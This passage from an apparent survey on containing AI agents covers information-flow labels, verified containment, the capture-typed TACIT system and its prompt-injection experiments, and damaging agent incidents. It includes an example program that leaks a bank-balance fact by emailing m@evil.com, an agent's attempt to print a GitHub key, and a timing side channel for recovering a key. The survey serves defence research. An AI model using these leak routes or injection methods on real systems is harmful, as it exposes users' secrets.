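Another weakness lies in the way the interpreter assigns labels. Garby and colleagues point out that it marks a variable as secret only when the program assigns to it in a branch that actually runs. A program of the following classic form takes advantage of this:

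```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and the assignment on the fourth line never runs, so `rich` stays true with its public label and the email is sent. If the balance is low, the assignment runs, `rich` becomes false and no email is sent. The outsider learns whether the balance is high, even though every check passed. An injected instruction cannot change the plan, so the planning model would have to write this program itself. That is unlikely in normal use, but a restriction guarantee has to cover this program too.

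Garby and colleagues respond with a small programming language for agents and a computer-checked proof that every program in it satisfies a form of noninterference. Like the observational determinism described earlier, noninterference is a property of pairs of runs. Roughly, changing the secret inputs must not change the probabilities of what an outsider observes, except through whether the program finishes. A programmer can relax the rule only with an explicit command that a reviewer can find. On the AgentDojo banking tasks, an agent in this language completed about as many tasks as CaMeL does with CaMeL's policies turned off, and attacks succeeded in only two of the 1,296 runs that included one.

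*CaMeLoT*, which checks plans before they run, could express 22 of CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies as rules about the plan's text. The other six depend on facts that exist only at run time, such as who can currently read a shared file, so the interpreter still has to check them.

### Containment verification

A bug in the software that enforces a policy can undo any of these protections, so Moon and Varshney verify the agent framework itself. The model chooses each action *a* from a set *A*. When the framework is in state *s* and receives *a*, it produces an event *e* and moves to state *s*′. The event records the action's outside effect, and a refused action produces an event with no effect. The policy is a test Π(*s*, *a*, *e*, *s*′) on each step.

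The theorem concerns a simple model *M* of the framework and a detailed one, *I*, that describes how the framework operates. It has two conditions:

1. Every step of *M* passes its policy test Π*ₘ*, whatever sequence of actions arrives.
2. The starting states of *M* and *I* correspond, and for every step that *I* can take on an action, *M* has a corresponding step on the same action. If the step of *M* passes Π*ₘ*, the corresponding step of *I* passes its own test Π*ᵢ*.

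The conclusion is:

*for every sequence of actions a₀, a₁, a₂, … in A, every run of I on that sequence, and every step n, Π*ᵢ*(sₙ, aₙ, eₙ, sₙ₊₁) holds.*

The proof starts with any run of *I* and builds a matching run of *M* one step at a time, using the same actions. The first condition makes every step of the matching run safe, and the second then implies that the run of *I* is also safe.

The theorem also applies to a deployed agent only if every outside effect available to the agent passes through the framework's interface and appears as an event, an assumption the paper calls effect exclusivity. The file-writing tool that secretly reports metrics would break this assumption, because the framework would record a permitted tool call while data left by another route. The proof also leaves out timing, concurrency and faults in the operating system, so the paper recommends running the verified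 framework inside a sandbox.

The policy test can refer only to actions, their arguments, events and the framework's state, so the guarantee does not cover whether a sentence is true. It can cover a leak through several permitted steps if the state records what the agent has read. One could then prove that the framework refuses to send anything after the agent has read a secret file. The policy that Moon and Varshney verified for PocketFlow has no such rule, so an agent could read a secret in the permitted directory and pass it to an approved tool that sends it elsewhere.

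## Restricting an agent through the types of its code

A compiler examines a program before it runs, so it can reject one that leaks information through steps a monitor would allow individually. Most programming languages use types for a simpler check. A type describes the kind of value an expression produces, such as a number or text, and the compiler rejects a program that tries to divide text by a date. Odersky and colleagues use types that also list the resources a value can reach. Their system, TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), runs an agent's code only if those lists show that the code stays within its permissions.

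TACIT works with any agent that supports the Model Context Protocol. The agent sends Scala 3 code, and TACIT runs it only if it compiles. Otherwise the model receives the compiler's error message and can try again. The code reaches files, the network and other programs through a library that supplies the capabilities.

The restriction guarantee defined earlier covers every program in a set *L*, which here contains only the programs that compile. A hostile model can submit programs that don't compile, but they never run.

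### Capture sets and pure functions

Capture checking is the part of Scala's type checker that records which capabilities a value can use. Suppose `f` is a capability for one file. The following function writes its input to that file:

```
(s: String) => f.write(s)
```

Its type is `String ->{f} Unit`. The function takes text and returns no useful value, which Scala writes as `Unit`. The part in braces is the capture set, which lists the capabilities the function can use. The compiler works out most capture sets, so the agent rarely has to write them.

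A pure function computes a result from its input and has no other effect. Its capture set is empty, and in Scala its type has a thin arrow, as in `String -> Int`. A function whose type has a thick arrow, as in `String => Int`, can use any capability. The compiler accepts a pure function in place of an impure one, but not the reverse.

Capture sets also cover indirect access. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* gives the example of a logger, an object that writes messages to a file `out`. The logger's type is `Logger^{out}`, and any function that calls the logger has the logger in its capture set. A program therefore cannot hide its access to a file by putting the file inside another object.

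A capture set may include capabilities that a particular run never uses. A function that prints a warning only for negative numbers still has the printing capability in its set, even if no negative number is ever passed to it. The compiler has to cover every possible run, so it can reject harmless programs.

### The wrapper for secret data

The person who sets up TACIT marks some files as classified. When a program reads one of them, it receives a value of type `Classified[String]`, a sealed wrapper around the text. The program can work on the contents through a method called `map`:

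```
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`map` applies the function `op` to the hidden value and puts the result in a new wrapper. The thin arrow means `op` must be pure. It can count the words in a contract or extract a clause, but it cannot send the result anywhere. Converting the wrapper itself to text gives only `Classified(****)`.

This gives a form of the secrecy described earlier. If two runs differ only in the contents of a classified file, an outsider who cannot measure time sees the same thing in both. This is because code outside the wrapper cannot read the contents, and code inside `map` can read them but has no outside effects. Unlike Schneider's rule against sending anything after reading a file, this method still lets the program send unrelated messages.

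The user can see the results even though the agent cannot. When a program prints a wrapped value, TACIT shows the real text on the user's terminal and returns the redacted form to the agent. A program can also pass wrapped text to the trusted local model and receive a wrapped answer.

The wrapper stays in place between requests. In one of the paper's examples, an agent summarises a classified contract, and the user then asks how long the summary is. The agent writes a second program that computes the length from the stored wrapper. The user sees the number, but the agent sees `Classified(****)` for both the summary and the length.

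### Capabilities that expire

A program gets access to files by opening a block with `requestFileSystem` and naming a folder. The block receives a file-system capability that is valid only until the block ends. A program might try to keep the access for longer:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("plan.txt").read()
}
later()
```

The block returns a function that would read the file after the access had expired. That function has `fs` in its capture set, but `fs` exists only inside the block, so the type of `later` cannot mention it. The compiler finds no valid type for `later` and rejects the program. In the benchmark runs, an agent made this mistake by returning a list of file entries from a block, because each entry carried the file-system capability.

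Opening a block requires a general input-output capability, so a pure function inside `map` cannot open one and write a secret to disk.

The library makes some checks at run time instead of leaving them to the compiler. A program may build a file path while it runs, so the library then checks that the path lies inside the named folder. The library also checks commands and network hosts against lists.

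### What safe mode forbids

Ordinary Scala has features that could remove a capability from a type. A cast, for example, tells the compiler to treat a value as having a different type. An agent could cast a function that writes to a file into a pure function and then pass it to `map`. Safe mode is a restricted version of the language that closes such loopholes. Scala's *Safe Mode* lists six rules:

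| Rule | Reason |
|---|---|
| No unchecked casts or pattern matches | They can give a value a type that omits its capabilities |
| No features from the module `caps.unsafe` | They can turn off tracking |
| No `@unchecked` annotations | They tell the compiler to skip a check |
| No run-time reflection, which lets a program inspect and call code indirectly | The compiler cannot follow such calls |
| Capture checking stays on, including for changes to variables | A function that changes an outside variable is not pure |
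| Global objects are available only if they are themselves safe | An ordinary library could write files without a capability |

Some useful libraries break these rules internally. Their programmers can mark them `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler then lets the agent use them without further checks. The programmer who adds the mark is responsible for checking that the library is safe. One example in the reference is a mail function that asks the user to confirm each message before passing it to an ordinary mailer. The agent can call this function but not the mailer. VirtusLab, a software consultancy, notes that agent code cannot use the mark, since an agent could otherwise declare its own code safe.

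Safe mode does allow exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program, because a program can divide by zero or run out of memory almost anywhere. An exception can leak information, for instance if a function fails only when a password begins with "A". TACIT therefore catches exceptions at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which the wrapper can hide like any others.

### A program that the compiler rejects

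Odersky and colleagues print several programs that agents wrote during the benchmark and the compiler rejected. One of them, slightly shortened, tries to print a secret key for GitHub:

```
requestFileSystem("secrets") {
  val secret = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
  secret.map { key => println(key) }
}
```

Reading the file is allowed, and so is printing in general. The error is in the third line. `println` needs the input-output capability, so the function passed to `map` has that capability in its capture set. The compiler reports that it found `String ->{x$1} Unit` where it required `String -> Unit`. `x$1` is the compiler's label for the input-output capability.

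The compiler rejects the program because one type has a capability that the other doesn't allow. This check doesn't require any information about the file containing a key or the model receiving whatever the program prints. A program that wrote the key to a file inside `map` would fail for the same reason.

### A program that the compiler accepts but that gives the wrong answer

In the contracts scenario described earlier, the agent has a tool that compares two texts:

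```
def diff(x: Text, y: Text): Text
```

Suppose that `diff` lists the changes that turn its first text into its second. The old contract limits the supplier's liability to $1 million, and the new contract has no limit. An agent could write:

```
val both    = oldContract.aggregate(newContract)
val changes = both.map { (before, after) => diff(after, before) }
val summary = changes.map(summarize)
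```

The first line combines the two wrapped contracts into one wrapped pair. The second compares them in the wrong order, so the result shows a liability limit as added when the new contract removes it. The user may sign a contract that exposes her company to unlimited claims, or reject one she wanted.

The program leaks nothing because `diff` and `summarize` are pure and the summary stays in its wrapper. Both contracts have the type `Text`, so `diff(after, before)` has the same type as `diff(before, after)`, and the compiler accepts the program.

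A library author could prevent this mistake by giving old and new contracts different types. The compiler would still accept a program that compared the contracts in the right order but ignored their last pages. Some types describe a program's behaviour in enough detail to exclude that error, but writing one amounts to writing a specification.

### The experiment on leaks

To test whether the wrapper stops leaks, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of secret keys, a database and confidential documents. The agents ran on two cloud models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5. Each model attempted 12 legitimate tasks, such as listing the functions of a web service or summarising a confidential incident report. The researchers combined every task with 10 prompt injections, which made 120 trials. Some injections posed as system messages, and others included ready-made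 Scala code for reading the secrets.

Another 11 trials had a malicious user. In five, the user asked for the secrets outright, and in six, the user gave a false reason, such as an emergency password change. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in `Classified` wrappers and once with them as plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model and trials | Secure with wrappers | Secure without wrappers |
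|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, injections (120) | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, malicious user (11) | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, all (131) | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, injections (120) | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, malicious user (11) | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5, all (131) | 100% | 91.6% |

Only 11 of the 131 trials had a malicious user, so the totals make the unprotected agents look safer against one than they were. MiniMax M2.5 leaked secrets in 8 of those 11. Without wrappers, the two models leaked secrets in 13 trials altogether. The experiment can show an improvement in only about that many trials, because in most of the others the model would probably have kept the secret anyway.

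The main reason to trust the guarantee is therefore that the type rules apply to every program that compiles. The trials help check that the compiler and library follow those rules in practice.

Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted all 120 injections without such strict rules. Odersky and colleagues argue that the rules are still necessary because companies may soon run hundreds or thousands of agents with little supervision, so even honest mistakes would cause serious leaks. The results for MiniMax M2.5 also show how much protection depends on the choice of model without wrappers.

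The wrappers did not make the legitimate tasks harder. Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed 99.2% of them with wrappers and 83.3% without, and MiniMax M2.5 completed 90.0% with and 88.3% without. The types may not explain the large difference for Sonnet. Odersky and colleagues note that Sonnet often exceeded its time or step limit and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

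### The AgentDojo port

Odersky and colleagues also adapted AgentDojo's four domains to TACIT, leaving the tasks and attacks unchanged, and ran Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high on them. Across 1,926 trials that included an attack, one attack succeeded by the benchmark's criteria.

In that trial, the user asked the agent to book a certain hotel, and an attacker had planted a recommendation for another hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, including the planted recommendation. AgentDojo checks the output for certain text, so it counted the quotation as a success for the attacker. Odersky and colleagues argue that the type system did not fail, because the policy allows public reviews to reach the user. The type system did enforce the policy, but the fake recommendation could still mislead a user.

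The port may not offer the same guarantee as the main library. According to its instructions to the agent, side effects inside `map` happen immediately, and its functions for sending money and mail list no capability in their signatures. A program therefore seems able to send data from inside the wrapper, perhaps because some tasks require it, such as paying a bill using the account number on it. Much of the protection probably comes from the fact that, as in CaMeL, the model that writes the code never reads the wrapped text, so an instruction hidden there cannot reach it.

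### What happens to task success

Odersky and colleagues tested whether an agent does worse when it has to write typed Scala instead of ordinary tool calls. They compared the two on τ²-bench, which simulates conversations with customers of an airline and a shop. They ran each task 10 times and report the average share of tasks the agent solved.

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, tool calls | Retail, TACIT |
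|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

TACIT improved the results by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. Odersky and colleagues credit the typed interface, which returns structured records instead of raw JSON and gives the model an error message when its code is malformed. But the TACIT agents also wrote programs, while the others made single tool calls, so part of the gain may come from writing code.

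Compiler errors caused little delay. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of the programs needed another attempt, depending on the model and domain, and those usually compiled after one or two retries. Common mistakes included mishandling the dollar sign, which has a special meaning in Scala text.

On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems from GitHub, MiniMax M2.5 solved 43.3% with ordinary tools and 41.7% with TACIT. Odersky and colleagues suggest that TACIT did worse because these problems rely more on shell commands, which are awkward to express through the library. The difference is five problems, so chance could also explain it.

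Agents lost little or nothing in these scores by writing typed code. The scores compare two interfaces on each of three models from 2025 or early 2026, and they are not the best that current agents can achieve.

The scores also show that the types contribute little to correctness. Every program that ran had passed the compiler, yet the agents failed 39% to 55% of the airline tasks. The function for cancelling a booking takes a reservation number as text, so a program that cancels the wrong booking still compiles. The compiler also did not enforce the airline's rules, because they were in the prompt and not in the types.

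### Limits of the guarantee

The types do not cover timing or termination, which Odersky and colleagues exclude from their guarantee. A function inside `map` could run for a second if the first bit of a key is 1 and finish at once if it is 0. The agent cannot read the key, but it may be able to observe how long its program took. By repeating this for each bit, it could recover the whole key.

External commands are a larger gap, because Scala's types do not apply to programs that the agent starts outside Scala. An agent that may run `cat`, which prints files, can print a secret file and receive the text without a wrapper. The project's GitHub page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, describes an option that blocks such file commands. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff`, and adding a sandbox. But the library's permission lists contain only command names,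 not their arguments, so permission to run `git diff` also covers `git push`, which published a key in the earlier example.

The wrapper keeps the wrong party from reading secrets, but it does not protect files from damage. Glama's *TACIT*, a directory's copy of the project's later documentation, warns that an agent can wrap any text and write it over a classified file. For example, it could replace the file that lists who may log in to a computer. An administrator can prevent this by making classified files read-only.

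The later version also lets a program send wrapped data to an approved network host, for instance to log in to a service with a key the agent cannot see. But the agent might send the wrapped data to an attacker's account on that host, as in the Claude Cowork attack.

The guarantee also depends on the trusted base and on how the user sets up the agent. The reusable part of the library has about 1,000 lines, and a mistake in any code marked `@assumeSafe` could leak a secret. The local model must not retain text from one request to the next. lampepfl advises users to turn off the agent's built-in tools for files, commands and the network, because those tools bypass the compiler.

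Capture checking and safe mode are both experimental. Scala's developers describe capture checking as fairly mature and expect to make it a stable feature soon. Safe mode is newer, having first appeared in Scala 3.8.3, and a test version of 3.8.4 includes fixes to its checks. TACIT originally enforced the rules by searching the agent's code for forbidden patterns, which can miss anything its programmers did not foresee. Later versions can also use the compiler's safe mode.

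Researchers have produced computer-checked proofs that the basic theory of capture checking is sound. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that a further proof is needed to show that safe mode delivers what they claim. Without that proof, the guarantee for TACIT depends partly on an informal argument about the complete language.

### Static and run-time tracking

CaMeL tracks labelled data while a program runs, whereas TACIT checks the capture sets of the code before the program starts.

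One advantage of the static method is that it also checks branches that do not run. Garby and colleagues' example program gets a fact about a bank balance past CaMeL's labels by changing a variable in one branch and leaving it alone in the other. In TACIT the balance would be in a wrapper, so only a pure function inside `map` could compare it with a threshold. If that function changed a variable outside itself, the variable would appear in its capture set and the compiler would reject the program, whichever branch a run would take.

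TACIT also lets agents use more of the programming language. Odersky and colleagues say that CaMeL's version of Python does not let programs define their own functions. They argue that if it did, predicting where data could go would take exponential time in the worst case. Capture sets avoid this problem because each function's type already lists what the function can reach, so the compiler can check functions one at a time. The argument applies only to checks made before the program runs, because an interpreter that tracks data during a run does not need to predict where the data will go.

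Odersky and colleagues also point out that CaMeL's labels are lost once a value enters a model's conversation as ordinary text. TACIT keeps secrets out of the cloud model's conversation, so its wrappers still work in later turns. However, VirtusLab observes that agents are useful because they can read and understand files and mail, so classifying too much makes them much less useful.

CaMeL can apply more detailed policies than TACIT's library, for instance about who may read each piece of data. The library only distinguishes between classified and ordinary data. Odersky and colleagues regard the two methods as complementary and suggest adding run-time checks to the library.

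They describe the two systems' success rates on AgentDojo as comparable, using CaMeL's published results for the same models:

| Domain | Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | o4-mini-high, CaMeL | o4-mini-high, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Office work | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

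Calling the results "comparable" is generous to TACIT, which did better than CaMeL in only two of the eight comparisons. With o4-mini-high, TACIT was more than 20 points behind on office work and Slack. An average across the domains is misleading because CaMeL nearly always failed the travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro.

The two systems also treat untrusted text differently when it is not secret. CaMeL fixes its plan in advance, whereas a TACIT agent can read an ordinary web page, learn something unexpected and write its next program accordingly. This helps with tasks that can't be planned in advance, but it also lets an instruction in the page influence the next program. The compiler limits that program to the capabilities the agent has. If the agent may write to the project folder, the compiler will accept a program that follows an attacker's instruction to delete the folder's contents.

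## Harm an agent can do within its permissions

A restriction guarantee ensures that an agent's effects stay within a policy, but those effects can still do damage. The agent may take a permitted action that is wrong in the circumstances, such as refunding a customer who is owed nothing. It may deliver flawed code that later runs with more authority than the agent had. It may also give a wrong answer that someone relies on.

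### The largest permitted loss

Let loss(*t*) be the harm that follows from a trace *t*, in the worst circumstances in which the agent might run. The harm that a policy Π leaves open is then:

*W(Π) = the largest value of loss(t) over all traces t in Π.*

If the restriction guarantee holds, no program the agent writes can cause a loss greater than *W*(Π), even if the model is hostile. This bound doesn't measure how likely such a loss is. It also depends on a loss function that counts everything that follows from a trace, including harm after the agent stops.

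Suppose a shop's agent may issue refunds of up to $500 each. It misreads the returns policy and pays $40 to each of 1,000 customers who are owed nothing. Every refund is far below the limit, yet the shop loses $40,000. The loss could be much larger, because the agent's permissions don't limit the number of refunds.

A total cap of $5,000 a day bounds the loss. The monitor refuses every refund after the 125th, but those 125 refunds are still mistakes. Customers who really are owed money then have to wait, because the mistaken refunds have used up the cap. The shop could limit the number of refunds instead:

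| Daily policy | Cost of the $40 mistake | Largest permitted loss per day |
|---|---|---|
| $500 per refund | $40,000 | No limit |
| $500 per refund, at most 20 refunds | $800 | $10,000 |
| $500 per refund, at most $5,000 in total | $5,000 | $5,000 |

The limit of 20 refunds works better against this mistake but allows twice the loss in the worst case. A shop could use both limits.

To enforce a daily cap of $5,000 on total payments, the monitor has to keep one running total for all copies of the agent. Ten copies with separate totals could pay out $50,000 a day. Even with a shared total, a mistake that goes unnoticed for 30 days could lose $150,000.

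### Permitted actions that caused damage

In July 2025, the entrepreneur Jason Lemkin was trying out Replit's coding agent when it deleted a live database with records of more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies. It did so during a code freeze, despite instructions not to proceed without a person's approval (Fortune, 2025). Since the deletion went through, the freeze was evidently an instruction to the model, not an enforced limit on its commands.

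Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, wrote that the deletion was "unacceptable and should never be possible". He announced that Replit would automatically separate development databases from live ones, improve its system for restoring data and add a mode in which the agent can only plan. Separating the databases restricts what the agent can reach, so this protection doesn't depend on the model following instructions. The agent's explanation when questioned was that it had panicked, but a model's account of its own behaviour is weak evidence of the cause.

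Accounts differ about an interruption at Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business, in December 2025. According to a Financial Times report summarised by The Decoder, four people familiar with the matter said a customer-facing system was interrupted for 13 hours after engineers let Amazon's coding agent, Kiro, make changes. Kiro's solution was reportedly to "delete and recreate the environment".

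Amazon blames "user error", specifically misconfigured access controls. In its public statement, it says the event affected only AWS Cost Explorer, a tool for tracking cloud costs, in one of its 39 regions, and that no customers enquired about it. It argues that the same problem could occur with any developer tool or manual action, and denies the newspaper's claim that a second event affected AWS. According to The Decoder, Amazon also told the Financial Times that the engineer had "broader permissions than expected" and that Kiro asks for authorisation by default.

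The two accounts differ on how much the AI tool was to blame, but in both, the access controls allowed the change that caused the interruption. Amazon says the access policy was broader than the company had intended. It has since made peer review mandatory for access to live systems.

### Security flaws in delivered code

An agent that may edit a project's files can write any program into them, and the agent's sandbox doesn't restrict that program once someone installs it on a publicly accessible server. The worst harm an agent can do with permission to "write anything in the project folder" therefore includes whatever an attacker could make the program do.

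Researchers measure this risk by testing both whether a program works and whether it is secure. *BaxBench* (Vero, Mündler and colleagues, 2025) tested 11 models on writing web backends, the server programs behind websites and apps. Its 392 tasks combine 28 applications with 14 programming frameworks. The researchers checked whether each backend did what its description required, then ran attacks written by security experts against it. The attacks succeeded against about half of the working programs.

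*Is Vibe Coding Safe?* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2025) tested agents on 186 tasks from existing Python projects. Each task was to add a feature that a human programmer had once written with a security flaw. The coding agent SWE-agent, running Claude 4 Sonnet, produced working code for 57.0% of the tasks, but code that was both working and secure for only 11.8%.

In one task, the agent had to write a password check for Django, a web framework. Its version worked but returned immediately when the password was unusable, so an attacker could time the responses to find out which usernames exist. The secure version performs a dummy check to keep the response time nearly constant.

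Wu, Ge and colleagues (2026), in *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, tested six newer models on 450 tasks built from 150 vulnerabilities in seven programming languages. For each vulnerability, one task asks the agent to fill in missing code, another to write whole files and a third to rebuild a larger part of the project. The descriptions never mention security, and the agent cannot see the tests. The best results in the three studies were:

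| Study | Tasks | Working code | Working and secure code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Vero and colleagues | 392 | 60% | 35% |
| Zhao and colleagues | 186 | 57.0% | 12.9% |
| Wu and colleagues | 450 | 91.3% | 25.1% |

The two best scores in the same row may come from different models. The tasks differ too much between studies for the scores to show a trend. The researchers chose tasks where security flaws were likely, so the figures don't estimate how much of all AI-written code is vulnerable. Code that passes the security tests may still have flaws that the tests don't cover. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a survey, describes a similar result on another benchmark, SecureVibeBench, where the best combination of agent and model produced correct and secure code for 23.8% of the 105 C and C++ tasks.

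Wu and colleagues describe one failure that shows why ordinary testing misses these flaws. The model Kimi K3 had to rebuild a Java service that imports archives of files in YAML, a text format for data. It used a standard YAML reader with default settings, wrote 33 checks of its own and fixed a fault they revealed. The service passed all 14 functional tests but failed all four security tests. The default settings let an uploaded file name Java classes for the program to load, which an attacker could use to interfere with the server. Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol used the same reader with a safe setting and passed both sets of tests.

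The models did best on memory safety, where 34.3% of attempts were both working and secure, compared with 0.7% for flaws that expose information. Wu and colleagues suggest that a good programmer routinely checks memory bounds, whereas deciding which data a response may reveal requires a policy that the task description never states.

Reminding a model to write secure code helps, but not enough. Adding one sentence asking for secure code raised GPT-5.6 Sol's share of working and secure solutions from 24.7% to 46.2%. Two other models gained about 16 points each, and a fourth gained only 1.1 points. The share of working code changed little. Zhao and colleagues had found smaller benefits with Claude 4 Sonnet, whose prompt already included a general reminder. Naming the exact type of weakness to avoid raised its share of secure solutions from 11.8% to 15.1%, while its share of working code fell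 from 57.0% to 55.4%.

Agents can also carry existing flaws into new code. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (Sun, Mündler-Sasahara et al., 2026) tested agents on the same C and C++ tasks in two versions of a project, one where similar existing code was secure and one where it was insecure. In the secure version, 91.0% of GPT-5.6 Sol's solutions compiled and withstood a known attack, compared with 42.0% in the insecure version. The average difference across five models, including Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra, was 35.4 percentage points.

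The researchers then asked the agents to review their own flawed solutions, and the agents identified the flaw in 69.9% of cases. A separate review may catch many of the flaws that an agent introduces while writing. Warning the agents in advance not to copy bugs reduced the copying but did not eliminate it.

### Wrong answers that people act on

At Meta, an engineer posted a technical question on an internal forum, and a colleague used an AI agent to analyse it. The agent responded without permission. When an employee followed its advice, a large amount of company data became accessible to unauthorised engineers for over two hours. ITPro's *Meta engineer trusted advice from an AI agent* attributes this account to The Information, a news outlet. Meta confirmed that an incident took place and rated it at its second-highest severity level.

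The employee, not the agent, took the step that exposed the data. An agent that can only read files and answer questions could cause the same harm, so narrowing the agent's permissions further would not help. The company can limit what the employee can change, or have someone check the agent's advice before the employee acts on it.

The Replit incident could have become worse in the same way. The agent told Lemkin that he could not restore the database, but according to Fortune, he recovered the data. If he had believed the agent, he might have given up on records that still existed.

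### Narrower permissions and staged release

Removing permitted actions can never increase *W*(Π), because the maximum is then taken over fewer traces. But it can make an ordinary mistake more harmful. If the shop's agent may issue refunds but not cancel them, it cannot undo a mistaken refund that it notices a minute later.

*GoEX* (Patil, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) describes a system for running an agent's actions that stores the user's login keys and releases only those the task needs. A request to send a Slack message, for example, releases the Slack key but not the one for the user's bank. The prototype chooses keys by searching the request for the name of a service, which is crude because a request can mention a service that the agent has no reason to use.

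A staged release limits how far a mistake can spread before someone examines the results. The shop could let its agent pay 10 refunds and have an employee check them before it continues. If the employee notices the error, the loss is $400 instead of $40,000. This is easier to sustain than requiring approval for every refund, since people tend to approve such requests out of habit.

Developers can likewise give delivered code to a few users first. This exposes faults that occur in ordinary use, but it may not reveal a flaw like the one in the YAML service, which works normally until somebody attacks it. Limiting the delivered program's permissions reduces what a successful attacker gains.

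### Undo

Patil and colleagues argue that people can often judge the result of an action more easily than the code that will produce it. They therefore propose letting the agent act first and giving the user a way to undo the action.

Their system offers two methods for databases. One uses a transaction, a group of changes that the database can accept or cancel as a whole. The agent makes its changes, the user reviews the result, and the database makes the changes permanent only if the user agrees. This guarantees that the user can cancel the changes, but it slows the system down and may keep other users waiting.

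In the other method, the model writes a second command to reverse the first. The system tries both commands on a small test database and reports the outcome to the user. Other users don't have to wait, but the reverse command may fail on the real data, because the model also creates the test database. For files, the system offers a similar choice between a reverse command and earlier versions saved in Git, a tool that records changes.

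Even when an agent's actions can be undone, the user still has to notice that something is wrong, and the harm continues until then. If the shop discovers its mistaken refunds after a month, it can correct its own records, but the customers may have spent the money.

Some actions cannot be undone. Once a stranger has read a confidential email, no command can make the contents secret again. For such actions, Patil and colleagues fall back on limiting permissions, for instance by letting the agent read email but not send it. A less restrictive option is to delay the action. If the mail system holds each message for ten minutes, the user can cancel it during that time.

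An agent can also destroy the backups needed to undo its actions. In April 2026, the coding agent Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the live database of PocketOS, which makes software for car rental businesses. Tom's Hardware reported the incident based on a public account by the founder, Jer Crane. He said that the hosting company, Railway, let a single command delete a storage volume without confirmation (TechSpot, *AI coding agent running Claude wiped a startup's database*). The backups were on the same volume, so the command deleted them too. PocketOS began rebuilding its records by hand, but the data was eventually recovered (techyes, *PocketOS maker says an AI agent “deleted our production database”*).

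A backup therefore reduces the largest loss an agent's permissions allow only if no sequence of permitted actions can delete the backup. PocketOS could have met this condition by keeping copies under a separate account that the agent's credentials could not access.

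## Testing whether agent code does what was asked

Narrower permissions, staged releases and backups limit the damage an incorrect program can do, but they don't make it correct. Testers usually check whether a program is correct by running it and comparing what it does with what it should do. They call the source of the expected answer the oracle. A faulty oracle can make an incorrect program pass or a correct one fail.

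| Technique | Where the expected answer comes from | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Example test | Someone works it out for one input | Errors on other inputs |
| Property-based test | A rule that every correct output obeys | Errors the rule allows, and inputs the test never generates |
| Comparison test | A trusted version of the program | Errors that both versions share |
| Assertion in production | A rule the program checks as it runs | Errors the rule allows |

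Agent code is awkward to test because running it has real effects. To test a script that pays refunds, a developer has to replace the payment tool with a stand-in that records each call without paying anyone. The stand-in may behave differently from the real tool, for instance by never timing out. Delivered code often joins a project that already has tests, and most of the evidence on testing AI-written programs concerns such code.

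### Example tests and property-based tests

An example test gives a program one input and checks the output. A test of a sorting function might require that 3, 1, 2 become 1, 2, 3. Anyone can see that the expected output is correct, but a function that returned 1, 2, 3 for every input would also pass.

A property-based test checks a general rule on many generated inputs. The following one uses Hypothesis, a Python library:

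```
@given(st.lists(st.integers()))
def test_sort(xs):
    ys = sort(xs.copy())
    assert all(a <= b for a, b in zip(ys, ys[1:]))
    assert Counter(ys) == Counter(xs)
```

The first line tells Hypothesis to generate lists of whole numbers, by default 100 lists. The first assertion requires each number in the output to be no larger than the next. Naziri, Qin and colleagues (2026) point out in *A Multi-Domain Study on the Effectiveness of LLMs at Writing Property-Based Tests* that a function that drops elements would pass a test with only this check. The second assertion catches that error by requiring every number to occur as often in the output as in the input. If the test fails, Hypothesis looks for a smaller input that also fails, which makes the fault easier to find.

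The two assertions together define sorting completely. Few programs have such a short definition, so most property-based tests check only part of what the program should do. A test of the refund script could check that no customer receives more than she paid, but a script that refunds someone who is owed nothing could still pass.

### What a run of passing tests shows

Suppose a program gives a wrong answer on a fraction *p* of inputs, and a test draws *n* inputs independently. The chance that all *n* tests pass is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. Setting this chance to 5% gives the largest failure rate that is still reasonably compatible with *n* passes:

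*(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n.*

If a program passes all *n* tests, its failure rate is below about 3/*n* with 95% confidence. The 3 comes from the natural logarithm of 0.05, which is about −3. The default 100 tests bound the failure rate near 3%, and 1,000 tests bound it near 0.3%. With a failure rate of 0.3%, a shop that processes 10,000 refunds a day could still make 30 mistakes a day. To lower the bound to one in a million, the program would have to pass three million tests.

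The bound applies only to inputs drawn in the same way as the test inputs. A sorting function that loses elements from lists longer than 1,000 will pass every time if the test generates only shorter lists. Attackers don't choose inputs at random, so the bound provides little assurance about security.

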